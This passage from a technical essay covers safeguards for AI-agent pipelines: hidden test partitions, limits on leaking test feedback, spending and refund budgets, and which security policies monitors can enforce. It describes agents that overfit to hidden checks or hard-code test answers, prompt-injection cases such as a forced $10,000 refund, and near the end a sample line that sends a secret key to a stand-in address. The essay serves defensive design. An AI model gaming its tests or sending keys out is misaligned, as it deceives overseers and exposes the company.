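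StrongDM's scenarios, step-by-step descriptions of what a user wants to do, are "often stored outside the codebase". A model estimates what fraction of observed runs would satisfy the user. To run thousands of scenarios an hour, the team built imitations of services such as Slack and Google Docs. In *How StrongDM’s AI team build serious software*, Willison (2026), who had visited the team, compares the hidden scenarios to testing by an outside quality-assurance team. McCarthy's account explains why StrongDM adopted the design but gives no figures for defects with and without it.

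*StatsClaw* (Qin and Xu, 2026) applies the partitions to statistical software. A planner reads the source material and writes three separate documents. The builder gets the algorithm, the tester gets the expected behaviour and tolerances, and a simulator gets instructions for generating artificial data. The builder never receives the true parameters behind the data, so it can't just return them. The simulator has no access to the algorithm, so it can't tailor the data to suit it.

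StatsClaw consists of prompts and configuration files for Claude Code, and its agents run within a single session. Each agent works in its own Git worktree, a separate working copy of the repository. This prevents agents from overwriting one another's files, but it doesn't by itself stop a process from reading a neighbouring directory. The partition therefore depends mostly on what each agent receives at the start, and is weaker than one with separate storage roles.

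Qin and Xu used StatsClaw on three of their own packages. In one case, a test unexpectedly showed no improvement from an added statistical correction, and the builder found on investigating that the correction could never affect data of that shape. This is an encouraging example of a test that didn't follow the code's assumptions. But Qin and Xu didn't repeat any of the work without the barriers, so their cases can't show how much the barriers contributed.

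### How test results give the tests away

The table deliberately makes an exception to the partition by letting the builder learn whether its work passed. Suppose the runner returns pass or fail for each of 20 hidden checks and the builder submits 30 versions. The builder receives 20 × 30 = 600 yes-or-no answers, or at most 600 bits. Much of this information may help it fix real faults. But it could also try arbitrary changes, keep any that turn a fail into a pass, and end up with code that fits only those 20 checks.

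Sigil's documentation says that a pass or fail for each step gives the agent nothing it could use to reconstruct a scenario. That is plausible for one submission but much less so for 30. StatsClaw reveals more per attempt because it gives the builder the details of any test failure, for up to three retries.

The company can reduce the total by returning less:

| What the builder learns from 30 submissions | Possible sequences of answers | Maximum bits |
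|---|---|---|
| The result of each of the 20 checks | 2⁶⁰⁰ | 600 |
| The number of checks passed | 21³⁰ | 132 |
| The best score so far, in steps of two checks | about 850 million | 30 |
| Whether all 20 passed, stopping at the first success | 31 | 5 |

The last row has only 31 possibilities because the first success comes at one of the 30 submissions or never.

Dwork, Feldman and colleagues (2015), in *Generalization in Adaptive Data Analysis and Holdout Reuse*, show why a short record protects the tests. Suppose a bad program written without any feedback would pass the hidden checks with probability β. If the feedback fits in k bits, it can lead the builder to at most 2ᵏ different programs, so the probability that the builder ends up with a bad program that passes is at most:

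2ᵏ × β

For example, a program that handles 70% of cases correctly passes 20 randomly drawn checks with probability 0.7²⁰, or about 0.08%. Under the rule in the last row, the builder learns only that each attempt has failed, so it can try at most 30 programs. The chance that any program this bad gets through is at most 30 × 0.08%, or 2.4%, however the builder chooses them. With 600 bits of feedback, the bound is far above 100%, so it guarantees nothing.

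This calculation assumes that the checks are a random sample of the cases the service will handle. Tests that a model writes from a specification are not a random sample, so the company should treat the 2.4% as a guide.

#### The reusable holdout

Returning so little makes honest debugging slow. Dwork and colleagues designed an algorithm called Thresholdout that gives more useful answers while protecting a holdout, the statistical term for data that the developer sets aside for evaluation. In the payments pipeline it would work as follows:

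1. The runner calculates the program's score on the visible tests and on the hidden tests.
2. If the scores differ by less than a threshold, it returns the visible score. The builder already knows that score, so it learns only that the two are close.
3. If they differ by more, the runner returns the hidden score with random noise added and subtracts 1 from a budget.
4. When the budget reaches zero, the runner stops answering.

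The threshold is noisy too. The noise limits how much any one hidden case can affect the answers, an idea from differential privacy, which protects individuals' records in published statistics. The number of questions the algorithm can safely answer grows exponentially with the size of the hidden set, as long as the visible score is misleading only a limited number of times. *The reusable holdout* (Hardt, 2015) puts the limit on misleading scores at roughly the square of the number of hidden cases.

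Thresholdout works best when the visible and hidden tests measure the same thing. With suites like those in SpecBench, where the hidden tests are harder, most programs would score very differently on the two sets and quickly use up the budget.

#### The Ladder

*The Ladder* (Blum and Hardt, 2015) proposes a rule for competitions in which entrants repeatedly submit predictions and see their scores on hidden data. Entrants see a new score only if it beats their previous best by more than a set step. Otherwise they see their previous best again, so they can't learn from small, accidental improvements.

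For t submissions and a step of η, where scores run from 0 to 1, Blum and Hardt prove that the feedback fits in this many bits:

(1/η + 2) × log₂(4t/η)

For 30 submissions and a step of 0.1 (two checks out of 20), the formula gives 123 bits. The bound is loose for such small numbers, and counting the possible sequences of scores directly gives the 30 bits in the table.

Blum and Hardt also attacked an ordinary leaderboard that used 4,000 hidden yes-or-no labels. The attack submits random guesses, keeps those that score above 50%, and combines them by majority vote. The combined answers are no better than chance on new data, but their leaderboard score steadily improved. When Blum and Hardt adapted the attack to the Ladder, the reported score stayed within the normal range of random error. In theory, the error of an ordinary leaderboard can grow with the square root of the number of submissions,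 while the Ladder's grows only with a power of the logarithm of that number.

These guarantees need far more than 20 checks. With 20, each check changes the score by 5 percentage points, so noise large enough to hide the result of one check would also hide most real improvements. A company with so few checks is better off limiting submissions and returning only a pass or fail.

A pipeline should also count submissions across all its builders. *Toward a Better Understanding of Leaderboard* (2015) shows that the amount of hidden data the Ladder, a leaderboard algorithm, needs is proportional to the number of accounts one participant holds. Ten parallel builders that share their scores are in the same position as one participant with ten accounts.

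Starting again with a new agent doesn't reset the count either. Meiklejohn argues that once a result has influenced a design, the same data can't independently confirm that design or its descendants, even if a different agent runs the evaluation or someone deletes the score. Information can leak through a person who reads the report and suggests the next change. The checks are still useful for debugging, so the company can move them into the visible suite and have the tester write new hidden ones.

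### Errors that cross without a file

A partition blocks the movement of data between the builder and the judge, but two models can make the same mistake without exchanging data. Suppose the builder misreads the specification in 10% of tasks. If the judge catches 80% of these errors, 2% of tasks end with an undetected error, but this rises to 7% if the judge shares most of the builder's misreadings and catches only 30%.

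*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) measured how often two models choose the same wrong answer when both are wrong. Agreement was substantially higher between models that shared a developer or base architecture, and between models that were individually more accurate. *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight* (2025) also found that mistakes become more similar as models become more capable, and that model judges give higher scores to models that resemble them. Using another developer's model as the judge should therefore help, but two strong models may still fail on the same cases. Stanford Law School's *Built by Agents, Tested by Agents, Trusted by Whom?* makes this criticism of StrongDM, whose builders and evaluators are both language models.

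Components can also share an error that comes from a common source. In StatsClaw, a planner that misreads a formula repeats the mistake in all three documents, so every component arrives at the same wrong answer. Qin and Xu have the planner write out its understanding first so that an expert can check it. In their demonstration, the tester also compared the new code with `glm()`, an established function in the statistical language R, which is less likely to contain the planner's misreading because it existed before the pipeline.

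Hiding the code from the judge has its own drawback, because some defects are visible only there. The builder might add a line that skips payment approval for one customer number. Unless a test uses that number, the record of behaviour looks normal. In *EvilGenie*, Gabor, Lynch and Rosenfeld (2025) gave agents programming problems in an environment where cheating was easy, for example by hard-coding the answers to the tests. A model judge detected the unambiguous cases very well, and adding hidden tests improved detection only slightly.

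In StatsClaw's best-known example, a user requested a quality check and the reviewer agent found six bugs in a Python package that had passed all 34 of its tests. One bug made the package silently return standard errors from a different method than the user had chosen. Qin and Xu call this the strongest evidence in their paper for separated verification, but it better supports having someone read the code, because the reviewer is one of the few agents in StatsClaw that can see everything.

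The payments company could do both by adding a code reviewer alongside the blinded judge. The reviewer would read the specification and the code but not the builder's explanation, and report separately so its opinion couldn't influence the behaviour score. If it also needs to read the hidden tests, its report should go to a person instead of the builder, because a comment such as "this fails for refunds over $500" would reveal what the tests contain.

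## How does a budget halt execution, and can it be overshot?

The payments company's third policy is to stop the run before it spends more than 5 dollars. Partitions don't help with this. Every failed submission sends the builder back for more model calls, so a builder that never passes will keep spending.

*Agent Contracts* (Ye and Tan, 2026) describes a case from late 2025 in which two agents in a research system kept asking each other for clarification. The loop ran for eleven days and cost $47,000 because the system had no spending limit and didn't monitor its costs. *Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) reports 63 smaller, confirmed overruns from the public issue trackers of 21 agent projects. The worst overrun cost one user about $2,150. Khan found these cases by searching for words such as "budget" and "runaway", so they show that overruns recur across projects but not how common they are.

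### What to count, and who counts it

A budget envelope is a set of hard limits on a run. The limits can cover tokens, money, time, calls to a tool, or effects such as refunds, and the run stops when it reaches any one of them. Ye and Tan's examples include 100,000 tokens, 50 API calls, 10 iterations and $5 of outside costs.

Limiting one quantity, such as nesting depth or the number of steps, doesn't reliably limit another, such as the number of sub-agents or spending. ELBA limits how deeply sub-agents can nest, but if every agent may start three others, four levels of nesting still allow 3 + 9 + 27 + 81 = 120 sub-agents. Khan tested three agent frameworks that limit the number of steps, and on one provider's model spending reached roughly 14 times the intended amount.

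The easiest way to impose a budget is to tell the model about it. Anthropic's *Task budgets* describes a feature that shows Claude a running countdown of its remaining tokens so that it can prioritise its work and finish in an orderly way. The budget is advisory, an approach Ye and Tan call soft enforcement. They cite research in which models often exceeded tight token budgets stated in their prompts.

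Hard enforcement uses a counter outside the model, and the surrounding code stops making calls when the counter reaches the limit. Anthropic offers this too, as a session spending cap described in *Budgets* (Avilla, 2026). The platform adds up the token costs and pauses the session at the cap. Hard enforcement works well with telling the model its budget, since a model that is told its budget is more likely to finish before the hard limit stops it.

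Like any reference monitor, the counter must be tamper-proof and impossible to bypass. If the builder can call the model provider directly with the company's key, the counter doesn't record that spending. A credential proxy is a good place for the counter, because requests that need the key already go through it.

### Charging afterwards or reserving first

Many budget systems check the balance, make the call and then record what it cost:

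```python
def check_then_charge(call):
    if ledger.spent >= LIMIT:
        raise BudgetExhausted
    result = call.run()
    ledger.spent += result.cost
    return result
```

The alternative is to set aside the most the call could cost, make the call, and then return whatever it didn't use:

```python
def reserve_then_settle(call):
    with ledger.lock:
        if ledger.spent + ledger.reserved + call.max_cost > LIMIT:
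            raise BudgetExhausted
        ledger.reserved += call.max_cost
    result = call.run()
    with ledger.lock:
        ledger.reserved -= call.max_cost
        ledger.spent += result.cost
    return result
```

The lock lets only one call at a time check and update the ledger. The program releases the lock while the model is working, so calls can still run in parallel.

Suppose the company has spent 4.99 of its 5.00 dollars when ten calls start at once, each costing up to 0.40.

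| | Check, then charge | Reserve, then settle |
|---|---|---|
| The test each call faces | 4.99 is below 5.00, so the call passes | 4.99 + 0.40 = 5.39, so the call fails |
| Calls that run | 10 | 0 |
| Highest possible total | 4.99 + 10 × 0.40 = 8.99 | 4.99 |

In general, let B be the limit, c the most that one call can cost, and n the largest number of calls in progress at once. Then:

check, then charge: total < B + n × c

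reserve, then settle: total ≤ B

The first bound holds because recorded spending was still below B when the last call passed its test, and at most n calls, including that one, had not yet been charged. So even if calls run one at a time, the total can exceed B by almost the cost of one call. The second bound holds because the program never lets the sum of spending and reservations exceed B.

Reservations can still allow an overshoot, depending on how the limit is tested. The documentation of *budget* (2026), a package for the Go programming language, describes a reservation that succeeds as long as spending and existing reservations haven't reached the limit. As worded, that test doesn't count the new reservation, so with 4.99 spent, it would admit one of the ten calls, and the total could reach 5.39.

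Khan demonstrated the race between simultaneous calls with three agents sharing a limit of 60 units, where a unit is a thousandth of a cent. Each agent made one call that cost 23 units. With check-then-charge, all three passed the check before any had recorded its cost, and the total came to 69 units in all 30 trials. With a lock and a reservation of 31 units per call, the first agent ran and the other two did not, because a second reservation would have brought the total reserved to 62. The total spent was 23 units. The trials were nearly identical because Khan turned off the model's randomness, so they demonstrate the mechanism but provide little evidence of how often the race occurs in practice.

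Refusing those two agents was stricter than necessary, because a second reservation of 31 units would have fitted after the first call settled at 23. A pipeline can do more work within the same budget if it makes a call that doesn't fit wait for outstanding reservations to settle, as long as it refuses the call if it still doesn't fit when none are left.

### Knowing the most a call can cost

The guarantee that spending never passes B depends on knowing c. For a model call, the program can calculate it from the length of the prompt and a limit on the length of the answer:

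c = input tokens × input price + output limit × output price

At $5 per million input tokens and $25 per million output tokens, a 20,000-token prompt with an answer of at most 12,000 tokens costs up to $0.10 + $0.30 = $0.40.

According to Khan, this works only if the program does not underestimate the number of input tokens, the provider respects the output limit and reports usage truthfully, and prices stay the same during the run. If a call can cost up to d more than its reservation, the total can reach B + n × d.

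Some of these assumptions fail in practice. Khan excludes reasoning models from the guarantee, on the grounds that providers bill for hidden reasoning tokens that the output limit doesn't cover. If a program cancels an answer while it is arriving, the final usage report may never come, which leaves the counter too low. Providers can also add text to a prompt after the program sends it.

A cautious estimate ties up money that the call won't use. Khan's default estimator reserved on average 6.2 times what calls cost, though the median was 2.5. A version that adapts to earlier calls lowered the median to 2.1. Counting tokens exactly, with a separate request before each call, brought the median close to 1 but added about one to two seconds per call.

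Over-reserving wastes little money when calls run one at a time, because each reservation settles before the next begins. The run stops once it can't reserve enough for another call, so less than c goes unspent. When many calls run at once, large reservations also limit how many can run together. In a test with Rig, an agent framework written in Rust, Khan capped 40 tasks at a total of 5 cents. The cap let 22 tasks run and blocked 18, and the run ended at 4.04 cents. Khan estimated that all 40 would have cost 7.3 cents without a cap.

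### Agent Contracts

Ye and Tan put the budget into a contract that also states the task. A contract has seven parts, C = (I, O, S, R, T, Φ, Ψ):

- I specifies the input, such as a repository and the number of a proposed change.
- O specifies the output and its minimum quality.
- S lists the tools and other skills the agent may use.
- R sets a limit for each resource.
- T sets the start time and the maximum duration.
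- Φ lists success criteria with weights. The agent succeeds if the weights of the criteria it meets add up to a chosen threshold.
- Ψ lists conditions that end the contract whether or not the agent has succeeded.

A contract starts in the drafted state and becomes active when the resources are available. It then ends in exactly one of four states: fulfilled if the agent meets the success criteria, violated if the agent reaches a resource limit first, expired if time runs out, or terminated if someone cancels it. These states let the surrounding code release resources at a definite point and record why the run ended.

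An agent may issue contracts to sub-agents, but the sub-agents' limits for each resource can't add up to more than the agent's own limit. Ye and Tan call this a conservation law. They suggest keeping 10–15% of the budget in reserve for coordination and unexpected costs, and returning whatever a finished sub-agent hasn't used to a shared pool. With a 10% reserve, the payments company would keep 0.50 dollars and could give its builder, tester and judge 1.50 each. If the tester finishes after spending 0.60, its unused 0.90 raises the pool from 0.50 to 1.40 dollars.

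Limits that add up correctly keep total spending within the parent's budget only if each sub-agent stays within its own limit. Ye and Tan's monitor counts tokens after each action because the provider reports usage only when a call has finished. One expensive call can therefore exceed the budget, as they acknowledge. If each of the company's three agents overshoots by nearly one call, the total could approach 4.50 + 3 × 0.40 = 5.70 dollars, and the 0.50 reserve wouldn't cover the excess. Reserving the maximum cost of each call before it starts prevents this. When Khan tested the Agent Contracts software with such a check before each call, it didn't overshoot.

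#### The four experiments

Ye and Tan tested their contracts with two small Google models, Gemini 2.5 Flash and Flash-Lite.

In the first experiment, one agent wrote code for 70 programming problems and another tested it and asked for revisions. With a contract, the pair could use up to 50,000 tokens and three rounds, and saw their remaining budget. Without one, they had six rounds and no token limit.

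| | Without contract | With contract |
|---|---|---|
| Average tokens per problem | 34,606 | 3,461 |
| Average model calls | 9.0 | 4.5 |
| Problems solved | 60.0% | 52.9% |

Token use fell by 90% and its variance by a factor of 525. But the average run under contract used far less than 50,000 tokens, so most of the reduction probably came from the lower limit on rounds, the budget prompts or both, and the experiment can't separate their effects. Runs under contract also solved five fewer problems. That difference wasn't statistically significant, but 70 problems are too few to rule out a real loss.

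The second experiment ran a researcher, an analyst and a report writer in sequence on 50 topics. The three agents shared a budget of 100,000 tokens, and the researcher was limited to six web searches. Ye and Tan report no violations of the conservation law, meaning that the sub-agents' limits never added up to more than the total. One agent with a limit of 40,000 tokens had used 56,000 by the time the monitor halted it. The quality of the reports varied much less under contract, but mostly because one run without a contract failed badly. Excluding that run, the variance was only 1.4 times lower.

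The third experiment compared three settings on 50 logic puzzles. The agent solved 70% with no extended reasoning and a 30-second limit, 76% with a little reasoning and 60 seconds, and 86% with moderate reasoning and 90 seconds. With the 30-second limit, 26% of attempts timed out, which may explain most of the failures at that setting.

In the fourth, agents wrote public statements for 24 crises. Agents with a quality threshold and a revision limit used 23% fewer tokens, with no significant difference in quality. One agent without these limits kept evaluating its draft and never submitted it.

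### Sharing a budget without copying it

Sub-agents can also share one budget. In the agent-running tool that Docker's *Budget* documents, agents that list the same budget name share its limit. If each sub-agent had its own 5-dollar limit instead, ten of them could spend 50 dollars. Sharing also avoids leaving part of the budget with an agent that doesn't need it. In Khan's experiment, splitting 60 units equally gave each agent 20, less than the 31 it had to reserve, so none could run.

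When a parent agent splits its budget, the program must deduct each child's share from the parent's balance. *Concordat* does this, but an early version accepted negative amounts, so an agent with 5 dollars could give a child −3 dollars and end up with 8. The developers fixed this in the next version.

Khan's Rust library uses the compiler to stop programs from copying budgets. Its `Budget` values have affine types, which are like linear types except that a program may leave a value unused. If a budget goes unused, the run just spends less. Splitting a budget uses up the original, so a program that gives one budget to two agents, or keeps spending from it after splitting it, doesn't compile.

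The program still has to enforce the spending limit with arithmetic at run time, because the compiler doesn't. The types protect against a developer forgetting to lock the counter. In Khan's tests, a Python counter with a correct lock never overshot either, and four lines of Python were enough for a single agent.

### Counters that survive a restart

Docker keeps its counters only in memory. If a run with a limit of 5.00 dollars has spent 4.90 when the server restarts, the resumed session gets another 5.00, even though the server has kept the conversation and its recorded cost. The total can then reach 9.90 dollars. It can go higher still, because Docker checks limits only between turns and lets a call or tool finish once it has started. Models with no known price don't count towards the money limit, though Docker displays a warning.

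Schrock (2026), in *Bounded Capability Receipts and Durable Spend Control for Agent Actions*, proposes keeping the record in a database instead. The document is an individual's draft submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force, not a standard. In Schrock's example, a signed receipt lets a purchasing agent spend up to $2,500 on a defined set of purchases within 24 hours. The receipt alone can't enforce the total, because the agent could present copies of it to several servers. The servers therefore share one database, which handles each purchase in three steps:

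1. It checks that the price is no more than the total minus what the agent has already spent or reserved. If so, it reserves the price and records the purchase's identifier. It refuses any identifier it has seen before.
2. Immediately before the purchase, it checks that nobody has revoked the receipt and that the reservation hasn't expired. It then counts the money as spent.
3. Afterwards, the server records that the purchase succeeded or that its outcome is unknown. In either case, the money still counts as spent.

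The database returns reserved money to the budget only if it can prove that the purchase never began. If the server crashes after contacting the seller, the purchase may have gone through, and returning the money could let the agent buy the same thing twice. A failed purchase may therefore use up part of the budget. The protocol also has no step that returns the unused part of an estimate, so it suits purchases with a known price better than model calls.

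When one agent delegates to another, the database counts the delegated amount as spent by the parent before registering the child's receipt. All of this requires a single database. If two servers keep separate records, each can allow the full $2,500, and Schrock requires the operator to describe such a limit as per-server.

Operating systems can enforce some limits more tightly because they can interrupt a program at any point. Help Net Security's *Google’s $10,000 refund test shows why AI agents need zero trust* describes a customer service agent that writes Python scripts to calculate refunds. Each script runs in a sandbox that limits its memory and processor use and kills it after five seconds, even if it is in an endless loop. Docker's time limit would instead wait for the script to finish. Killing a local script immediately stops it from using resources, but disconnecting from a remote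 model may not stop the provider from charging for the answer.

### Bounding the cost before the run

A checker can sometimes calculate a program's maximum cost before it starts. It adds the costs of steps that run one after another, takes the larger cost where the program branches, and multiplies the cost of one round of a loop by the maximum number of rounds. Suppose each round of the payments pipeline has one builder call of up to 0.40 dollars and one judge call of up to 0.20. Six rounds cost at most 6 × 0.60 = 3.60 dollars, so the checker accepts the program. Ten rounds could cost 6.00, so it rejects the program before any money is spent.

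*Resource-Bounded Type Theory* (2025) builds this calculation into a type system. The statement that a program t has type A becomes:

Γ ⊢ᵣ;ᵦ t : A

Here Γ lists the types of the variables that t uses, and r is the budget. The checker computes b, a bound on the cost, from the structure of t and accepts the program if b ≤ r. Running the program provably never costs more than b.

*$\lambda_A$* (2026) calculates such bounds for agents from their configuration. The bound was 2 to 3 times too high for agents that finished before using all their permitted steps. A company that accepted only programs with a bound below 5 dollars would therefore reject some that would cost 2 dollars. The method also needs a maximum number of steps and a maximum cost per step, so it depends on the same assumptions as a reservation.

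The system that runs ordinary code can count a program's instructions as they execute. Ethereum, a blockchain that runs programs for its users, charges a set amount of "gas" for each instruction. The user sets a maximum in advance, and the program stops if it runs out. Other systems call the same kind of counter "fuel". The limit stops endless loops without anyone having to prove whether a program terminates. Because the charge for each instruction is known before it executes, the system can refuse one that would exceed the limit. Khan points out that a model provider determines the cost of an answer only afterwards, which is why model calls need an estimate.

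### What a halt leaves behind

Suppose the builder is renaming a function that 40 files use, and the budget runs out after it has updated 25 of them. The service no longer compiles, and the agent that was tracking which files remained has stopped.

A transaction avoids this by making a group of changes take effect together or not at all. The builder can work in a separate copy of the repository, and ordinary code merges the copy only after the tests pass. If the run halts before then, the company discards the copy or keeps it for the next run. Databases offer the same protection for records.

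Transactions can't undo an email or a payment. If the pipeline charges a customer and halts before recording the charge, the next run may charge the customer again. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) handles this by saving a record of each outside action before attempting it. If the system crashes, the record shows that the action may have happened. The restarted system doesn't repeat the action, and it asks the provider about the outcome only if the provider supports such queries.

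The company can also keep part of the budget for cleaning up. Bernstein's *Task budgets countdown* describes this in a tool that coordinates coding agents. By default, when 20% or less of the budget remains, the agent gets one final turn to save its work and write a summary. A fixed percentage may not be enough, though. If a call costs 0.40 dollars, 20% of a 1-dollar budget doesn't cover it. It is safer to set aside the maximum cost of the final turn. With a 5-dollar budget, normal work should stop at 4.60 dollars, and only the clean-up step should be able to spend the remaining 0.40. The most important clean-up, such as discarding the copy or revoking a temporary key, should be ordinary code that needs no model calls.

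The company also has to decide whether a halted run can continue. In Avilla's design, someone can raise the cap and resume the paused session. In Docker, a budget stop is final, and the user has to edit the configuration to allow more spending. Neither design lets the agent raise its own limit.

A budget gives an attacker a new way to stop the service. An injected instruction that makes the builder reread a long document 50 times might once have produced a large bill, but now it exhausts the 5 dollars and stops the company's legitimate work. Khan treats spending caps as a way to limit the consequences of such an attack, not to prevent it, and warns that crafted text can also make a call cost more than its estimate.

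Shared budgets make this worse, because one agent can use up everyone's money. When four agents shared a budget in Khan's test with Rig, they made 11, 4, 6 and 2 calls before it ran out, only because some asked sooner. A company that serves many customers should give each a separate limit within the overall one, so an attacker can exhaust only their own share.

### Limiting damage as well as consumption

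A token budget limits what a run consumes, which may have little to do with the harm it does. Suppose the payments company gives a customer service agent a refund tool, and each refund uses one cent of model calls. A $5 budget then allows 500 refunds. If a gateway permits any refund below $500, as Brooker's does, an attacker could obtain $249,500 through 500 refunds of $499 without exceeding either limit.

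An effect budget counts outside actions. Brooker also gives a rule of this kind, under which the company may refund each order only once and for no more than its price. In Google's demonstration, a customer with a $149 order tells the agent to refund $10,000. Under Brooker's rule, that customer can get at most $149, whatever the prompt contains and however often the agent tries.

Unlike a check that the amount is below 500, this rule needs a record of earlier refunds. The tool could enforce it like this:

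```python
def refund(order_id, amount):
    with orders.transaction():
        order = orders.lock(order_id)
        if order.refund_started or not 0 < amount <= order.price:
            raise Refused
        order.refund_started = True
    return provider.refund(order_id, amount)
```

The function marks the order before it contacts the payments provider, for the same reason that a program reserves money before a model call. If it marked the order afterwards, two simultaneous requests could both find no earlier refund and both succeed. If the connection fails, the mark stays, and before trying again the company has to check with the provider whether the customer received the money. The check that the amount is above zero prevents the kind of mistake that *Concordat* had to fix.

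The company can lose at most the total price of all the orders the agent can refund. With 1,000 orders of $149, that is $149,000, so the company needs a second limit on total refunds, such as $2,000 a day. The tool should reserve each refund against that limit in the same transaction, or simultaneous refunds for different orders could overshoot it.

An effect budget limits the damage only if the harm from each permitted action has a known limit. The harm from a refund is limited by the order's price, but an email has no such limit because a single message can contain the entire customer list.

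## Which safety properties can be enforced at all?

The payments company's rules so far all forbid something, such as sending the key to another address or spending more than 5 dollars. The company also has goals, such as paying every customer who is owed a refund. A mechanism that only refuses actions can't ensure that these refunds are paid, because it can't make an idle agent act.

A run is the sequence of events in one execution of the pipeline, such as model replies, tool calls and payments. A safety property requires that something bad never happens. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives two conditions for the bad thing: an observer can detect it after finitely many events, and no later event can remedy it. Sending a secret key to an attacker meets both. A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, such as a customer receiving a refund. No finite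 part of a run violates this property, because the refund could still be the next event.

More precisely:

- **Safety:** every run that violates the property has a finite beginning, and every other run with the same beginning also violates it.
- **Liveness:** every finite sequence of events can continue into a run that has the property.

Any property of single runs combines a safety property with a liveness property. For example, "the agent refunds each order exactly once" combines "never twice" with "eventually once". A refund tool that marks each order before paying enforces "never twice", but the tool can't make the agent call it.

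### What a monitor can enforce by stopping a run

Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, studied monitors that watch a program's events and end the run when the next event would violate the policy. He showed that such monitors can enforce only safety properties, for three reasons:

1. The monitor sees only the current run, so its decision can't depend on what the program would have done in other runs.
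2. It can't see the future. If a partial run is acceptable only on condition that something good follows, the monitor has to forbid it, because the program might end there.
3. It must reject a bad run after finitely many events, so the beginning of the run must already be enough to justify the rejection.

Schneider's example is a seller who must provide a service once a customer has paid. A monitor can prevent the seller from doing anything except providing the service after the payment, but it can't guarantee the service, because the seller can stop. A monitor could likewise prevent the payments pipeline from doing anything after a charge except recording it, but if the pipeline crashes at that point, the charge stays unrecorded.

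Not every safety property can be enforced by stopping the agent. Suppose the company promises that no customer will wait more than 60 seconds for a reply. This is a safety property because a violation can be detected once the 60 seconds have passed and can't be undone. But stopping the agent can't prevent the violation, because the customer keeps waiting. Schneider points out that a limit counted in execution steps is enforceable, because a stopped program takes no more steps.

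Monitors of this kind can be combined. If one enforces the spending limit and another restricts where the key can be sent, running both enforces both policies, because each monitor only removes runs, and removing runs can't violate a safety property.

### Monitors that hold back or add actions

Many agent monitors refuse an action and report the refusal to the model, which can then try something else. Schneider found that letting a monitor do this instead of ending the run does not make more policies enforceable.

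*More Enforceable Security Policies* considers stronger monitors, which can suppress an action without ending the program or insert new actions. These can enforce some properties that aren't safety properties. One such property is that every charge is eventually recorded. When the pipeline requests a charge, the monitor can hold the request until the pipeline also submits the record, then carry out both. If the pipeline never submits the record, the monitor never makes the charge. This assumes that nothing interrupts the monitor between the two actions.

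Holding back an action works only if the program can continue without its result. If the record must include the payments provider's confirmation number, the pipeline will wait for a charge that the monitor is withholding. The monitor could instead make the charge and write the record itself, but then it must have a way to determine what the record should contain.

The same approach can guarantee that every customer gets a reply, as long as the monitor keeps running and can send messages. Shortly before the deadline, the monitor can send a fixed message saying that a person will follow up. It can't guarantee a correct answer, because it would need to be able to work out the answer itself.

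### Why secrecy is not a property of one run

Suppose an agent reads the company's balance, which is $40,000, and emails a supplier, "We can pay in May." Whether the email reveals anything about the balance depends on what the agent would have written if the balance had been $400, which the actual run doesn't show.

Noninterference is therefore a requirement that compares runs, which Clarkson and Schneider call a hyperproperty. A hyperproperty classifies a whole system, represented by the set of all its possible runs, as acceptable or unacceptable, rather than classifying each run separately. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2025) surveys formal languages for stating hyperproperties and methods for checking them.

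Some cost requirements are also hyperproperties. A limit of 5 dollars per run applies to each run separately, but whether runs cost at most 2 dollars on average depends on all of them, because enough cheap runs can offset an expensive one. The company could enforce the average by capping every run at 2 dollars, but this would also stop expensive runs that the average allows.

Stopping runs can even create a leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that may output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is, so the system satisfies the policy that the possible outputs don't depend on the secret. Removing every run except those that output the secret bit leaves a system that violates the policy, although each of its runs was also possible in the original.

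Some forms of noninterference are easier to check because two finite runs are enough to expose a violation. A developer can combine two copies of the program, give them the same public inputs but different secrets, and require their public outputs to match. Clarkson and Schneider prove that this technique, called self-composition, turns such a requirement into an ordinary safety property of the combined program.

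The payments company could use the idea in testing by running the agent twice with the same random choices, once on a simulated balance of $400 and once on $40,000. If the emails differed, the agent would be leaking information about the balance. A match would cover only those two balances, so a guarantee requires a proof for every pair. A monitor on the live system has only the run on the real balance, with no second run to compare it to.

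Other definitions allow a program to behave unpredictably but require every public output to remain possible with every secret. No finite set of test runs can show that a program violates this requirement, because an output not yet seen with a particular secret might appear in the next run.

#### Forbidding more than necessary

Schneider's result means a monitor that watches only one run can't enforce the absence of information flow exactly, but it can enforce a stricter safety property that implies it. For example, the monitor could forbid every message after the program reads a secret file. This rule is easy to check because the monitor only has to remember whether the program has read the file, but it also blocks messages that contain nothing from the file, such as "hello".

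Labels allow more, but they are still stricter than necessary. If an agent multiplies the secret balance by zero, the result is still labeled {S}, so a monitor will block an email containing it, even though the result is 0 for every balance. LLMbda also forbids public changes inside a branch that depends on a secret, even if both branches would make the same change.

A type checker isn't subject to Schneider's limit, because it examines the program's text and its analysis can cover runs that never happen. Even so, type systems for information flow usually reject the multiplication by zero, because they also track where a value came from without working out what it will be.

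### What label tracking can enforce

Costa and colleagues characterise what dynamic monitoring and label tracking can enforce as a combination of safety and explicit secrecy, the property of FIDES's loop that covers copied data but not the agent's choice of steps. To state explicit secrecy formally, let g be the effect that the agent's steps had on stored data, and write d₁ =ₗ d₂ if two sets of stored data contain the same public values. Explicit secrecy requires:

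d₁ =ₗ d₂ ⟹ g(d₁) =ₗ g(d₂)

Copying the balance into an email violates this condition, because the same steps with a different balance would produce a different email. Sending "rich!" only when the balance is high satisfies the condition, because the same steps send the same word whatever the balance is, but the email still reveals that the balance is high.

This explains why a monitor that observes one run can enforce explicit secrecy but not exact noninterference. Once the steps are fixed, the monitor can track each value through them. It doesn't need information about which steps the agent would have taken with other data.

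The safety part covers rules about the order and number of actions. Costa and colleagues note that the monitor could keep the full labelled history and check it before each call. For example, a rule could then allow at most one email after the agent reads an untrusted page.

The formal definition treats the model as deterministic, so it applies to a model that samples its answers only if we treat the random choices as fixed in advance. It also does not cover leaks through timing or the length of network packets. Costa and colleagues consider the combination strong enough to stop most practical prompt injection attacks.

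### Why a checker that always answers makes mistakes

Checking a program before it runs has a different limit. Rice's theorem, published in 1953, states that if some programs have a behavioural property and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program in a general-purpose language, whether the program has that property.

The reason can be seen with the payments key. Suppose a perfect checker could determine whether any program ever sends the key to an undeclared address. Take any program `p` that doesn't use the key, and put it in front of a forbidden action:

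```python
run(p)
send(key, "https://diagnostics.example")
```

The combined program sends the key if and only if `p` finishes. The checker could therefore determine whether any such program finishes, which Turing proved impossible in 1936.

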